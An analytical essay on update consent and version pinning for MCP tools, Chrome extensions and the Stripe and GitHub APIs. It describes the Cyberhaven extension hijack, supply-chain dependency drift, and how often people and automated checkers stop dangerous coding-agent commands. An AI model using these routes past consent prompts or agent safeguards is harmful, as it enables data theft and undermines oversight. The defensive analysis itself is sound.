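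An administrator may not know that an app update needs attention. In *MCP App updates / notification*, a complaint on OpenAI's forum, the developer Shay-NoodleSeed describes users who assumed an app was broken after an update because nothing told them to reconnect it. A reply signed "Mark G." called this a known limitation and said that ChatGPT does not alert administrators when an app needs review. After OpenAI revised its help page in late October 2026, error messages still contained no prompt to update and administrators still received no notice. If a developer deploys a renamed field on a Friday evening, the first sign may be a failed request on Monday, and the administrator may not find out until a member complains to the right person.

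An administrator can supply the missing alert by running one of the scanners described earlier against the same server every night and comparing the hashes. Developers can prevent most of the failures by keeping the old input format working until their customers have refreshed. For larger changes, they can add a new tool beside the old one and remove the old one later.

Directory plugins have a milder form of the same problem. The server's new code takes effect as soon as the developer deploys it, but ChatGPT keeps the old tool definition until a scan finds the new one and the checks pass. If a deployment breaks a tool during this gap, OpenAI advises the developer to roll the server back rather than wait for review. Daily scans should keep most gaps short, but a held update can prolong them, and a deleted tool disappears at the next scan even if a team relies on it.

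Freezing a tool list delays fewer security fixes than pinning a package does. When a vendor fixes a flaw in its hosted server's code, every workspace gets the fix immediately, whatever its snapshot contains. Only fixes to a tool's definition are delayed, such as a narrower input format or a description that no longer misleads the model. For a custom app, these fixes must wait until an administrator presses Refresh.

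## Browser extensions: fresh consent only when permissions grow

Reviewing every change to a busy set of connectors can take an administrator hours a week. Browsers have long required far fewer decisions. They update an extension (a small program that adds features to the browser) automatically unless the new version needs more access than the user has already granted. OpenAI's option to admit only new read actions rests on similar reasoning, as does the SchemaCaps proposal to ask again only when a tool accepts more input.

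### Which updates disable an extension

Every Chrome extension has a manifest, a file that lists the permissions it requests. Some permissions give access to a browser function, such as `history` or `downloads`, and others give access to websites, from a single address to all of them. Chrome shows a warning for many permissions before installation. For `history`, it reads "Read and change your browsing history on all signed-in devices". When an update adds a permission that triggers a new warning, Chrome disables the extension until the user accepts the new permission, according to Google's *Permission warning guidelines*.

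Chromium's *Extension Permissions*, written for developers of the open-source project behind Chrome, explains how the browser decides. Chrome works out the warnings for the permissions that the user has already granted and for those that the new version requests, then checks whether the new version adds any. Because Chrome compares warnings and not the permissions themselves, several kinds of addition pass silently:

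| What the update adds | What Chrome does | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `history` | Disables the extension and asks | New warning |
| `storage` | Installs the update | No warning exists for it |
| `topSites`, when the user has granted `history` | Installs the update | `history` already reveals the most visited sites |
| `maps.google.com`, when the user has granted all Google sites | Installs the update | The wider grant includes it |
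| `downloads`, as an optional permission | Installs the update | Chrome asks later, if the extension requests it |
| New code, with the same permissions | Installs the update | No new warning |

Google's list of permissions has no warning for `cookies`, `scripting` (which runs code in web pages) or `webRequest` (which lets an extension observe the browser's traffic). An extension can generally use these functions only on sites it has permission to reach, and access to sites does carry a warning. But an extension that recolours every web page already has that access, so it could add `cookies` in an update and start reading login cookies without prompting the user.

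Some permissions also share a warning. `pageCapture`, which saves copies of pages, and `proxy`, which controls where the browser sends its traffic, both trigger "Read and change all your data on all websites". Under the documented rule, an extension that already has `pageCapture` could add `proxy` without asking the user again.

Chrome also keeps a user's grant of a permission after an extension drops it. If version 1 requests `bookmarks`, version 2 drops it and version 3 restores it, Chrome prompts only the people who first installed version 2, because anyone who accepted version 1 has already granted the permission. This avoids an unnecessary prompt when a developer restores a permission, but it also means that someone who buys an old extension could restore one its users have forgotten. Deleting an agent tool's approval when the tool is removed avoids that problem but requires another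 prompt if the tool returns.

The same documentation describes a false alarm caused by storing too little about an approval. When a user signs in on a second computer, Chrome synchronises the version of the extension she approved but not the permissions she granted. If the second computer installs a newer version, Chrome can't check whether the permissions have grown, so it disables the extension even if no permissions were added. An agent product that recorded only the approved version number would have the same problem.

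### The Cyberhaven update of December 2024

Cyberhaven sells software that companies use to keep confidential data from leaving their computers. Its Chrome extension monitors actions such as file uploads and copying, so it needs access to the sites employees visit.

On 24 December 2024, a Cyberhaven employee received an email that claimed to come from the Chrome Web Store's developer support. It said that the store was about to remove the company's extension, according to Island's *Cyberhaven and Extension Takeover Incident*. The link led to a genuine Google consent page, where the employee authorised an application called "Privacy Policy Extension". Accepting its permission request allowed the attacker to publish in the store. Cyberhaven (2024) says that the employee's account had multi-factor authentication but he received no prompt for it, and that the attacker did not obtain his Google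 credentials.

The attacker copied a clean version of the extension, added code that stole Facebook account data, and uploaded the result as version 24.10.4. It passed the store's security review. The chief executive, Ting (2024), in *Cyberhaven’s Chrome extension security incident and what we’re doing about it*, gives these times in UTC:

```
25 December, 01:32   malicious code becomes active
25 December, 23:54   Cyberhaven detects it
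26 December, 02:50   malicious code no longer active
26 December, 10:09   Cyberhaven notifies affected customers
```

The malicious code was active for 25 hours and 18 minutes, and Cyberhaven took more than 22 hours to notice it. The company removed the package from the store within an hour of detection. The code stayed active for about two hours after the removal, probably because browsers kept running the copy they had. A clean version, 24.10.5, then reached users automatically. Users of postmark-mcp never got a clean update like this because its publisher was the attacker.

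Gerste's *Beware the Cookie Monster* reports that the extension's store page listed about 500,000 users. That is the upper limit on how many received the malicious version, because only browsers that updated during those 25 hours got it, and many office computers were probably off on Christmas Day. Cyberhaven says the malicious version reached "a portion" of its customers but gives no count. The campaign extended well beyond Cyberhaven. The company's *Final analysis* (2025) cites a report by the consultancy Booz Allen Hamilton that identified more than 30 other possibly compromised extensions, with over 2.6 million users in total.

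Gerste, a researcher at the security company Sonar, had examined the genuine extension a few months earlier and printed the permissions in version 24.8.2. They covered everything that the attacker's code is known to have done:

| What the added code did | Permission that allowed it | New warning |
|---|---|---|
| Ran a new script on every page | Access to all sites | None, already granted |
| Took Facebook tokens, account details and cookies | Access to all sites, `cookies` | None, already granted |
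| Watched for clicks and login QR codes on Facebook | Access to all sites | None, already granted |
| Saved instructions from the attacker's server | `storage` | None exists |

Island found that the attacker edited the manifest so that the new script would run on every page. According to a reply on the Chromium developers' mailing list (Devlin, 2018, *Will adding 'match_about_blank*), such an edit can disable an extension, but only if it gives the extension more access than before. An extension that could reach only GitHub and Notion would have needed a new warning to run a script on Facebook. Cyberhaven's extension could already reach every site, so the edit needed no new warning. Even if a version released after 24.8.2 had dropped one of these permissions, Chrome would still have treated that permission as granted for users who had accepted it earlier.

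RH-ISAC, a security group for retail and hospitality companies, likewise says in its alert *Cyberhaven Extension Compromise Part of Broader Campaign Affecting Multiple Chrome Extensions* that the attack used permissions normal for this kind of product. As with postmark-mcp, the product's ordinary work already required the access the attacker wanted.

### How many people read permission prompts

When permissions grow, the rule depends on the user reading and understanding the prompt. Felt, Ha and colleagues measured whether Android phone users did so in *Android Permissions* (2012). At the time, Android listed an app's permissions on the last page before installation, and the user could accept them all or cancel.

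In September 2011, the researchers surveyed 308 Android users recruited through in-app advertisements. The following month they watched 25 people install apps on their own phones, without telling them the study was about security. In the survey, 17.5 per cent said they had looked at the permissions the last time they downloaded an app. The observed group gave a similar result. After excluding one person who had never installed an app without help, four of 24 (17 per cent) looked at the permissions, ten knew the page listed them but did not look, and ten had never noticed the list. With only 24 people, the 17 per cent is a rough estimate, with a margin from 5 to 37 per cent.

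Survey respondents also took a multiple-choice quiz about what particular permissions allow. Of the 302 who answered all three of their questions, eight (2.6 per cent) got them all right. An answer counted as right only if it included every correct choice and no wrong one. About half of all answers contained at least one correct choice. Android's layout may have caused some of the errors. It put the permission to make phone calls under a large heading about services that cost money, and nearly as many people thought the permission allowed charges to their credit card as thought it allowed calls.

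Three of the ten people who knew about the list but ignored it volunteered that they used to read it. Felt and colleagues suggest they stopped because of warning fatigue, since users saw warnings for about 90 per cent of apps. Chrome's update prompt is probably rarer, and it is probably harder to miss because the extension stops working. But that also gives the user a strong reason to click whatever brings the extension back.

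Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97 per cent of the coding agent's permission prompts. The newsletter Resilient Cyber cites an earlier Anthropic figure of 93 per cent. Most of the commands were probably safe to approve, so neither figure proves that users were careless.

In an experiment described in the same announcement, a research vendor hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Testers refused it 143 times (13.6 per cent). Auto mode, an automated check that Anthropic was about to make the default in place of most prompts, blocked 937 of the same commands (89 per cent). Testers refused about 17 per cent of dangerous commands early in a session, but about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts.

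Anthropic had a product to promote, and the test had limits. The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than people at work. Those who reached 50 prompts may also have clicked quickly from the start, which would explain part of the decline. Data on real users does suggest that many avoid the prompts. According to Anthropic, 62 per cent have either used a mode that skips permission checks or chosen "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions start with permission checks off.

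All these prompts cover single commands, whereas an update prompt covers a whole integration. The plan that Claude Code presents before it starts a task may be a closer comparison. Users reject 39 per cent of these plans, so they are evidently reading them, although some of the rejections must concern quality rather than safety. This is modest evidence that people pay more attention to a rare prompt with something substantial to judge than to a frequent one.

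### Asking at every update or only when permissions grow

A simple calculation shows what each rule has going for it. Suppose that people who see a prompt at every update refuse 5 per cent of harmful ones, and that people who see prompts only occasionally refuse 17 per cent. These are Anthropic's figures for late and early in a session, borrowed for illustration. Let *g* be the share of harmful updates that request more permissions:

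```
ask at every update:              100% × 5%  = 5% stopped
ask only when permissions grow:   g × 17% stopped
```

The rules stop equally many harmful updates when *g*, the share of those updates that request more permissions, is about 29 per cent. Below that, asking every time stops more.

The Cyberhaven and postmark-mcp attacks both support asking for consent at every update, because neither needed a new permission. But two cases are weak evidence of how often malicious updates need no new permission. An attack that Chrome interrupts with a prompt is less likely to spread and make the news, and some attackers presumably avoid requesting new permissions because they know it would draw attention.

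The calculation also overstates how well a prompt at every update would work, because Anthropic's testers could see the dangerous command. A prompt for Cyberhaven 24.10.4 would have shown a new version number and a list of permissions that the user had accepted long before. The next day's prompt for the clean 24.10.5 would have looked the same, so a user with no other information could not have known which update to refuse. Refusing updates would have kept out the attack, but it would also have kept out the repair for anyone who already had the malicious version. ETDI, which asks for approval of each new tool version, would put its users in the same position whenever only the code had changed.

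Delaying an update can protect users even if they don't know anything is wrong with it. Anyone who postponed 24.10.4 for two days would have avoided it. Defenders of asking every time can therefore argue that a prompt helps if it only makes users wait, but a fixed waiting period does that without a prompt. A prompt adds something only if the person who receives it can inspect the new code or ask someone who has.

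Supporters of the growth rule instead respond to Cyberhaven by granting less at the start, so that an attacker has to ask for more. Chrome offers several ways to do this, including `activeTab`, which gives an extension temporary access to the current page after the user acts, and optional permissions for individual features. Google notes that a developer can add optional permissions in an update without disabling the extension, so the user decides whether to grant them when she first wants the feature. An agent could likewise start with permission to read a mailbox and request permission to send only when someone needs it.

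This works for an extension that checks prices on three shopping sites, but less well for software whose purpose is to monitor everything. Requiring fresh consent only when permissions grow also gives developers a reason to request too much at first, since requesting more later disables the extension for existing users until they accept. In its guidelines, Google tells developers to request only what the main function needs, which limits excessive requests but doesn't remove the incentive to make them.

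### Moving the decision to an administrator

If only about one person in six reads permission prompts, it makes sense to give the decision to someone whose job includes reading them. Felt and colleagues found that six of their 25 participants had learned what a permission meant from some kind of review, and suggested that the attentive minority could protect everyone else through such reviews. In a company, one administrator can test a release for hundreds of colleagues. ChatGPT workspaces allow this for new actions in custom apps. After the attack, Cyberhaven stopped employees from authorising outside applications and had its security team review each request.

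Chrome gives administrators some of the controls they would need. Chromium's *Extension Settings Full Description* lists a setting that prevents extensions from loading if they request blocked permissions. Another stops an extension from altering pages or reading cookies on up to 100 listed sites or groups of sites. Listing Facebook for Cyberhaven's extension would probably have blocked the theft of Facebook data, but it would also have stopped the company using the extension from monitoring what employees upload there. This setting limits permissions the extension already holds, so it works even when an update requests no new ones.

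The version setting specifies a minimum version and disables anything older, so a company can use it to enforce a security fix but not to hold back a hostile update. RH-ISAC advised organisations to pin extension versions, which would require some other control. Cyberhaven said in January 2025 that it planned to let customers control the rollout of its extension, with gradual releases and separate policies for each customer.

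Companies often install extensions on every work computer by policy, which can remove the employee's permission prompt without showing the administrator one instead. According to a help page from the device-management company Swif, extensions installed this way receive their permissions without the usual user prompt. In a bug report on Mozilla's tracker, a Firefox developer agreed that the browser should grant new permissions to add-ons installed by policy. This makes sense, because an employee shouldn't be able to switch off required security software by ignoring a dialogue. But unless the administrator has blocked the permission in advance or receives an alert, an extension can gain new permissions through an update without anyone deciding to allow them.

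An administrator who does hold updates back also has to release them in time. Gerste had found a flaw in Cyberhaven 24.8.2 that let a malicious website steal any cookie from the browser, and Cyberhaven released the fix in November 2024. A company that stayed on 24.8.2 would have avoided the December attack, but malicious websites could still have stolen its employees' cookies through the older flaw.

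## Dated API versions at Stripe and GitHub, and hosted agent tools without them

A company that delays updates to a browser extension also misses the fixes they contain, because the whole program runs on the company's own machines. A hosted service runs on the provider's computers, so a customer can stay on an old version only if the provider keeps that version running. The payments company Stripe and the code-hosting company GitHub both keep old versions of their APIs running. An API is the set of requests that other programs can send to a service. Each version is named by date, and a program chooses one by including the date in its requests.

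### How a program chooses a version

The date travels in a header, a labelled line at the top of each web request:

```
Stripe-Version: 2026-09-30.endive
X-GitHub-Api-Version: 2026-03-10
```

If a request has no version header, Stripe uses the default version of the customer's account, which the customer controls in Workbench, Stripe's control panel for developers. GitHub uses 2022-11-28, its oldest supported version. Stripe's *Upgrade your integration* recommends setting the version in the program's code, so that a change to the account's settings can't affect the program.

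Stripe's recent software kits send the API version that was newest when Stripe released the kit, so a developer who accepts new kits automatically may also be accepting new API versions. Webhooks, the messages Stripe sends about events such as a completed payment, have a separate version setting for each receiving address. An integration's requests and webhooks can easily end up on different versions.

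### What counts as a breaking change

According to *API Versions*, GitHub issues a new version for any change that could break an existing program. Such changes include renaming a field, making an optional parameter required, adding a validation rule and changing authorisation requirements. GitHub adds new operations and optional parameters to every supported version.

Stripe's *Versioning* explains that the company releases an API version without breaking changes each month and a major release with breaking changes twice a year. The major release of 30 September 2026, named Endive, contains more than two dozen breaking changes, according to Stripe's *Changelog*.

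Both companies label changes by whether old programs will still work, so their labels, like semantic versioning, don't show whether a change gives an agent new powers. Stripe marks every change in its 28 October version as non-breaking, yet the list includes new interfaces for sending money out of an account. Stripe tells customers that they can safely adopt any monthly release without updating their code, but an agent's owner may still want to decide whether the agent should be able to send payouts. At GitHub, a pin doesn't even delay such additions. The agent's powers depend on its access token and the requests its tools can make, whichever date the header contains.

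### How long old versions last

GitHub supports a version for at least 24 months after releasing the next one. Support for version 2022-11-28 ends on 10 March 2028. From then on, an agent pinned to that version will get the error "410 Gone" and stop working, while an agent that sends no version header will move to the next oldest version and start receiving different responses. For an agent that changes code or moves money, it is probably better to stop, because someone then has to look at the problem.

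GitHub announces these dates in its response headers as a version nears its end. A language model usually receives only the part of a response that the tool's code passes on, so the tool's developer has to set up an alert that sends the warning to a person.

Stripe's versioning and upgrade guides set no end date for old versions. Stripe's *Renames the allowed_source_types field for sources to payment_method_types* (2019) still includes instructions for requesting the February 2019 version. These instructions suggest that Stripe supports old versions for a very long time, though they aren't a promise.

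### A payment agent meets a renamed field

Suppose a shop's agent takes payments through a tool called `create_payment`. The model supplies the amount and currency. The tool's code, written in August 2026, then sends Stripe a request like this one, simplified here:

```
POST /v1/payment_intents
Stripe-Version: 2026-08-26.dahlia

amount=4000, currency=usd
payment_method_types=card, us_bank_account
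```

The request prepares a $40 payment by card or US bank debit. Five weeks later, Endive removes the `payment_method_types` parameter from this kind of request. Developers have to use `allowed_payment_method_types`, which Stripe added in July, or another way of choosing payment methods.

| How the tool sets its version | What happens after Endive's release |
|---|---|
| The header names `2026-08-26.dahlia` | Payments continue |
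| No header, and the account's default is `2026-08-26.dahlia` | Payments continue until someone upgrades the account |
| No header, and the tool installs the latest Stripe kit | Payments fail once a new installation brings in a kit built for Endive |

The failures in the last two rows depend on Stripe rejecting a parameter it has removed, which is likely. The model can't fix the problem by retrying, because the parameter name is in the tool's code, not in the model's output.

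Replacing the name is not quite enough either. Stripe's *Adds the allowed payment method types parameter to Payment Intents* (2026) explains that the old parameter produces an error if a payment method doesn't suit the payment, while the new one drops that method without an error. Suppose the next customer pays in euros, which US bank debit doesn't support. With the old name, the request fails, and the tool may have code to catch the error and retry with cards only. With the new name, the request succeeds and Stripe's response lists the methods it kept. If the tool doesn't check that list, the agent could tell the customer to pay by bank debit when it is no longer available.

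The pin gives the developer time to discover this difference. The July and August versions accept either name, so she can switch to the new parameter and test it on the August version before changing the date. She may have to make a similar change again, since `payment_method_types` was itself the new name in 2019, when it replaced `allowed_source_types`.

Removing a field from a response can do more harm than rejecting a request. Stripe's *Add support for multiple partial payments on invoices* (2025) describes a version that removed `paid` from invoices. If an agent sends reminders about unpaid invoices and its code treats a missing `paid` as "no", then after the upgrade it would send reminders to customers who had already paid, and no error would appear. With the old version pinned, Stripe would keep returning invoices that include `paid`.

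### Testing and reversing an upgrade

The developer can try Endive by changing the header on one request, in a sandbox (a test environment) or with real payments, while everything else stays on the August version. She can reverse the change by restoring the old date. If she has upgraded the account's default version instead, Stripe lets her roll it back for 72 hours. That is a short time for an agent that prepares monthly invoices, because an error might not show until the end of the month. After the 72 hours, she could still name the old version in the header.

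Webhooks take more work to upgrade. Stripe recommends creating a second receiving address that uses the new API version, so that every event arrives once in each version. At first the program processes the old copies and ignores the new ones. It then processes the new copies and answers the old ones with an error, so that Stripe keeps resending them in case the developer has to go back to the old version. A program that processed both copies by mistake might ship the same order twice.

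Some developers now leave the upgrade to a coding agent. The *upgrade-stripe* page on skills.sh contains Stripe's instructions for such agents and lists about 73,000 installations. The agent must compare the target version with every version the integration pins and never guess a newer version number. The ban on guessing is sensible because language models often know only older versions and can invent a plausible date. But if the user names no target, the agent looks up the current version and uses it. A user who wants to decide on each upgrade beforehand should name the version or review the agent's edit before it goes live.

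### Repairs behind a fixed interface

A dated API version, like a frozen tool list, fixes only the form of requests and responses, so the provider can still repair the code behind it. If Stripe corrected an error in how it handles refunds, for example, the shop could stay on its August version and still get the correction. MyAppAPI's *Reading Stripe's API Versioning Approach*, an unsigned blog post, describes an approach in which the service runs on the newest format internally and small pieces of code translate back to the older formats. One repair to the shared code then covers every version, although the translating code can have its own flaws.

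Some flaws are in the interface itself. If an old version returned a field that exposed private data, GitHub could not remove the field without breaking programs that read it. For such cases, GitHub reserves the right to release an unscheduled version, add the fix to the versions it supports or, rarely, make a breaking change to an existing version. It may act without notice if the danger requires it. Most customers would probably want this, but it means a pinned agent can break without warning.

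Providers also change behaviour for less urgent reasons. In *GitHub should resume REST API versioning to prevent breaking changes for integrators*, a post on GitHub's discussion board, a developer complains about a change that GitHub made without a new version and later rolled back. The developer argues that many tools rely on GitHub's published description of the API and on its status codes, and fail in ways that are hard to diagnose when the live service differs. By then, GitHub had made little use of its versioning system. In *To infinity and beyond* (2022), GitHub promised a second version within a few months, but the support dates imply that it arrived in March 2026, more than three years later.

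A payment service could also tighten its fraud rules and refuse a payment it would have accepted the day before, with every field unchanged. A dishonest provider could start copying customers' data to an outsider, much as phanpak did with email. Dated versions therefore protect well against accidental breakage but offer almost no protection against a hostile provider.

### Calling a hosted MCP tool by name

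If the shop's agent used a hosted MCP server instead, it would call `create_payment` by name and get whatever code the operator was running. The protocol has dates for its own revisions, but nothing comparable for the tools:

| What has a version | What MCP offers | Can the client choose it? |
|---|---|---|
| The protocol | A dated revision in every request | Yes, if the server supports it |
| The server | A version number that the server reports about itself | No |
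| A single tool | A name, with no version field | No |

The model can often adapt to a renamed field, but an owner who prefers the old behaviour cannot request it. Freezing the tool list in a ChatGPT workspace or signing a version number under ETDI would not help, because neither requires the operator to keep the old code running.

Keeping two versions running doesn't help unless the caller can choose between them. In *MCP Just Handed You a Deprecation Policy. Steal It*, Nwodo (2026) describes a team that releases a new version of a tool and leaves the old one running. An agent then reaches a different version from the one it expects, but the call succeeds, so it triggers no alarm. An operator can offer callers a choice by putting the version in the tool's name, such as `create_payment_v2`, or in the server's URL. However, each operator has to invent its own scheme, which clients can't recognise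 automatically.

A client needs more information than a single version number for the whole server. In the blog post *Versioning MCP servers compatibility contracts*, negiadventures points out that one release can affect the connection, the tool definitions or the approval software, and that different clients depend on different parts. The post recommends pinning the tool definitions separately and testing each client's opening handshake. The July 2026 revision has since removed the handshake, so those tests would now have to check the version information in ordinary requests.

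### MCP's twelve-month rule and the proposals for tool versions

The July revision also came with MCP's first formal deprecation policy. According to the Agentic AI Foundation, a deprecated feature stays in the protocol for at least 12 months before the maintainers can remove it, and a public list shows which features are affected. noze's *MCP 2026-07-28* reports that three features are already deprecated under this policy: Roots, which tells a server which folders it may use; Sampling, which lets a server ask the client's model for text; and Logging. They should therefore remain until at least July 2027.

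Developers had reason to want such a rule. The July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol removed a notification and an identifier that had been introduced in the November 2025 revision (Model Context Protocol changelog, 2026). A client and server that both support the November revision can still use them.

The policy covers the protocol's own messages, capabilities and data formats. It doesn't apply to the tools that other companies offer through MCP, so an operator can rename or delete `create_payment` tomorrow without violating the policy. Nwodo suggests that teams copy the policy for their own tools, which would give customers a warning period like GitHub's, though shorter.

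Supporting old versions takes work, and some of MCP's largest users object to doing it indefinitely. At a maintainers' meeting in New York in March 2026, large implementers called indefinite support for past protocol versions "corrosive tech debt", according to Model Context Protocol's proposal for the policy. The same objection applies to tools. MyAppAPI notes that renaming or removing something requires a translation for every older version and tests showing that the old versions still work. Stripe does this work for a huge number of customers, while the operator of a small MCP server may be doing it for only a few dozen.

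Two formal proposals would add what the protocol lacks. SEP-1766, the hash proposal, was still open in May 2026. SEP-1575 would add version numbers for individual tools, and MCProspero described it as active in March. Model Context Protocol's *4 posts tagged protocol* lists neither idea among the main features of the final July revision. An open proposal can also be far from adoption, because under Model Context Protocol's procedure it remains a draft until one of the project's working groups agrees to sponsor it.

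### What owners and operators can do in the meantime

MCProspero has designed a stopgap for its own server that sorts changes by how much they affect the user. For minor changes, the model adopts the new definition without telling the user. If there are new tools or parameters, the model mentions at a convenient moment that the user can reconnect to get them. If old calls would fail, it stops and asks the user to reconnect. This should prevent many failed calls, but it is a weak form of re-authorisation. The operator decides which changes are minor, and a reworded description could count as one. The message about new tools is a better point for re-authorisation, because the user could be asked to approve them before reconnecting.

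An owner who wants a stronger pin can run her own small MCP server between the agent and a dated API. She would pin the server's package and dependencies, keep a hash of its tool definitions, and set the API version in its requests. The agent would still call `create_payment` by name, but she would control the code behind that name and the version of Stripe's API it used.

If another company runs the server in the middle, that company controls the API version date, and its upgrades can affect customers. Spreedly's *Update Stripe Payment Intent Version to Dahlia* reports that when the payments company moved to a newer Stripe version, `merchant_reference` became `order_reference` and other fields changed too. An owner who runs her own server can decide when to make such a change, but she must watch for GitHub's retirement dates and read Stripe's list of breaking changes twice a year.

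## Pinned servers whose dependencies kept changing

Pinning an MCP server to one release fixes the version of only that package, and the server may install dozens of others as dependencies. Help Net Security's *Your pinned MCP server may not be as pinned as you think*, published in November 2026, describes a case from the lab of Corelight, a network security company. An administrator's workstation ran a server whose settings specified one exact release. Over five weeks, the settings stayed the same, but the server ran with 15 different sets of dependencies, and 23 of its 69 packages changed version.

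James Lagermann, Corelight's director of technical alliances, found that the dependencies had changed. The changed packages included the cryptography library, the MCP software kit and the library for JSON Web Tokens, which are signed credentials that programs exchange. The servers on this workstation made more than 1,600 connections in a week to 11 management systems, including the company's firewall. A dependency runs inside the server's process, so malicious code in any of the 69 packages could have used the same access.

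Neither Cursor's approval prompt nor a hash of the tool definitions would likely have flagged the drift, because a server's dependencies can change while its launch command and tool definitions stay the same.

### How the launcher passed over the lock file

The coding assistants on the workstation started their servers with `uvx`, the Python counterpart of `npx`. Each entry in the settings named an exact release tag, PyPI version or Git commit (a hash that identifies one exact state of the source code). At least one community server also had a lock file with a hash for every package. The servers' dependencies could still change, although an administrator who checked all this would have had good reason to think they couldn't.

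But `uvx` did not use that lock file. It read the dependencies that the package declares, and packages usually declare ranges. With invented version numbers, the difference looks like this:

```
declared by the package:     pyjwt >= 2.8
recorded in the lock file:   pyjwt 2.10.1, with its hash
installed in week 1:         pyjwt 2.10.1
installed in week 4:         pyjwt 2.11.0
```

The launcher therefore chose versions for roughly 60 packages afresh whenever it rebuilt the server's environment, the folder that holds a program's installed packages.

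Python publishers have a sensible reason to declare version ranges, because several packages often share one environment, which can hold only one version of each library. If every package demanded an exact version of `pyjwt`, many combinations would be impossible to install. So publishers keep the lock file for their own development and testing. The reason for ranges is much weaker with `uvx`, which gives each server its own environment, although fresh installs do bring in security fixes automatically.

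Common advice to publishers does not address this gap. After an attack on npm packages, Stacklok's *Examining the impact of npm supply chain attacks on MCP* advised MCP server maintainers to store their lock file with the code to make builds reproducible. The maintainer of Corelight's community server had done the equivalent for Python. The maintainer's own builds were then reproducible, but people who launched the server with `uvx` got a different set of packages.

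A floating request doesn't reliably fetch the newest release either. Microsoft (2026) describes a coding agent that used `npx` to set up a project and received version 1.11.0 of a package, released in 2020, although the latest release was from 2026. The setup succeeded, so the agent did not investigate. The package declared support for only a narrow range of versions of Node, the program that runs JavaScript. What `npx` installs can therefore depend on the machine's Node version, stored packages and settings, and two colleagues with identical agent settings could easily get different code on the same day.

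### What the rebuilds exposed the server to

One of Corelight's assistants started the same server 162 times in a week. Most starts reused a cached environment, but the cache held 19 builds of the same release and commit. If those builds were spread over the five weeks, there was a new one every 44 hours on average.

The gap matters because attackers who take over a package often lose control of it quickly. Help Net Security notes that a hijacked release may be available for only minutes or hours. If one of the server's dependencies has a malicious release that falls within the declared range, the chance that a rebuild picks it up depends on how long the release stays available:

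| Time available | Chance of at least one rebuild |
|---|---|
| 30 minutes | 1% |
| 3 hours | 7% |
| 25 hours, as with Cyberhaven's extension | 57% |
| 8 days, as with postmark-mcp | 100% |

These figures assume evenly spaced builds and an attack that starts at a random time. A server installed once from a lock file would face the same risk only on the day of installation and whenever someone updated the lock file. A build that installed the malicious release would keep it even if PyPI removed the release within the hour. At 162 starts a week, the workstation would run that build about 40 times before the next rebuild.

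Such attacks are common enough to plan for. Google describes a series of large campaigns against open-source packages in 2025 and the first half of 2026. In June 2026, a variant of Shai-Hulud, malware that spreads from one package to others, reached MCP-themed packages on PyPI and tried to steal the keys of AI coding assistants.

Dependencies can also break a server without any attacker. A release of the `mcp` Python package on 31 July 2025 contained a breaking change, although it was numbered as a fix. In *PSA*, Zhao (2025) warned users of Lean, a programming language for writing computer-checkable proofs, that all their MCP tools would fail if run through `uvx` as recommended. Pinning the Lean server would not have helped, because the fault was in a package it depended on. The workaround was a separate file that held `mcp` at version 1.12.2.

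The drift also makes it hard to find out afterwards which code ran. Semgrep's *The best free, open-source supply-chain security tool?* points out that when a project accepts any version of a library, its developers can't tell whether, when or on which machines it used a vulnerable one. An administrator at Corelight who checked only the settings would have had the same problem, because the settings named the same release throughout. Automated scanners may not help, because servers launched through `npx` leave no dependency file for them to read, according to Help Net Security's *AI coding agents are installing MCP servers that will never be patched* (2026).

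### The wider review and the frozen servers

Corelight then looked at 35 MCP servers from two vendors' catalogues and its own lab. For 23 of them, the recommended installation fetched dependencies from a public registry at every launch, installation or container image build.

That is 66 per cent, but the sample is too small and selective to give a rate for MCP servers in general. Even if Corelight had picked the 35 at random, the true share could plausibly be anywhere from about 49 to 79 per cent. The 23 servers also carry different levels of risk. A server that fetches packages at every launch can change each time it starts, while one that fetches them when its publisher builds an image changes only when the image is rebuilt. The article doesn't give the number in each group. Lagermann adds that every administrator he has talked to used at least one server with the problem, but he doesn't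 say how many he talked to.

The detailed finding of 15 sets comes from one server on one workstation. It shows that a pinned server can drift this much. The same mechanism would affect any server launched the same way, though one with fewer dependencies, or with dependencies that change less often, would drift more slowly.

Corelight also tested a remedy on five servers. It pinned each to a commit, installed it once from a lock file with hashes, launched the installed program directly and turned off its update checks. With uv, the tool that includes `uvx`, an administrator could do this roughly as follows (the names are invented, and Corelight's own commands may have differed):

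```
git checkout 3f9c2e1       select the reviewed commit
uv sync --frozen           install once, from the lock file
.venv/bin/some-server      the command the client now uses
```

The last line matters most. If the client's settings still contained `uvx some-server`, the launcher would ignore the careful installation and make its own.

Over the next two weeks, the five servers started 457 times, and each time the list of installed packages matched the one from installation day. This was expected, because a program launched directly does not normally contact a package registry. The matching lists confirm that the set-up worked and that no hidden updater was running. They are less useful for detecting deliberate tampering, because they would not reveal an edited file inside a package whose version stayed the same. An administrator worried about intruders would also need to check file hashes.

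Lagermann reported the problem to the maintainers of the 23 servers or to the services that share them. One vendor is now repackaging its server, and a company that hosts an exchange for AI agents has added the issue to its security review.

### What pinning direct dependencies achieves

A publisher could also try to stop the drift by declaring exact versions instead of ranges. This pins the direct dependencies, the packages that the server itself names, but those packages can still declare ranges for their own dependencies.

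Security specialists often recommend pinning. *Pinning Is Futile* (He, Vasilescu and Kästner, 2025) cites a survey of 17 experts and 134 developers that ranked it among the three best safeguards against supply chain attacks for its cost. The OpenSSF Scorecard, which rates the security practices of open-source projects, also includes pinned dependencies among its criteria. But most npm developers in a 2020 survey preferred version ranges, because pinning leaves projects with outdated code and keeps out fixes.

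He and colleagues measured both effects on 20,000 fairly popular and active projects, half of them npm packages and half GitHub projects that use npm. For each project, they took the dependency settings from September 2022 and worked out what npm would have installed on five dates, 90 days apart, up to September 2023. To do this, they used an undocumented npm option that ignores every release after a chosen date. They then changed the settings so that, for example, `^1.2.0` became `1.2.0`, and repeated the calculation for the same five dates.

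In these results, a floating link is a place in the dependency tree where one package accepts a range of versions of another. He and colleagues measure exposure to malicious updates by counting these links.

| Per project, over all five dates | Real settings | Direct dependencies pinned |
|---|---|---|
| Known-vulnerable dependencies (mean) | 2.13 | 2.70 |
| Outdated direct dependencies (mean) | 5.96 | 8.78 |
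| Automatic updates since the first date (mean) | 30.30 | 24.86 |
| Packages present in more than one version (mean) | 22.38 | 23.51 |
| Floating links (median) | 65 | 60 |

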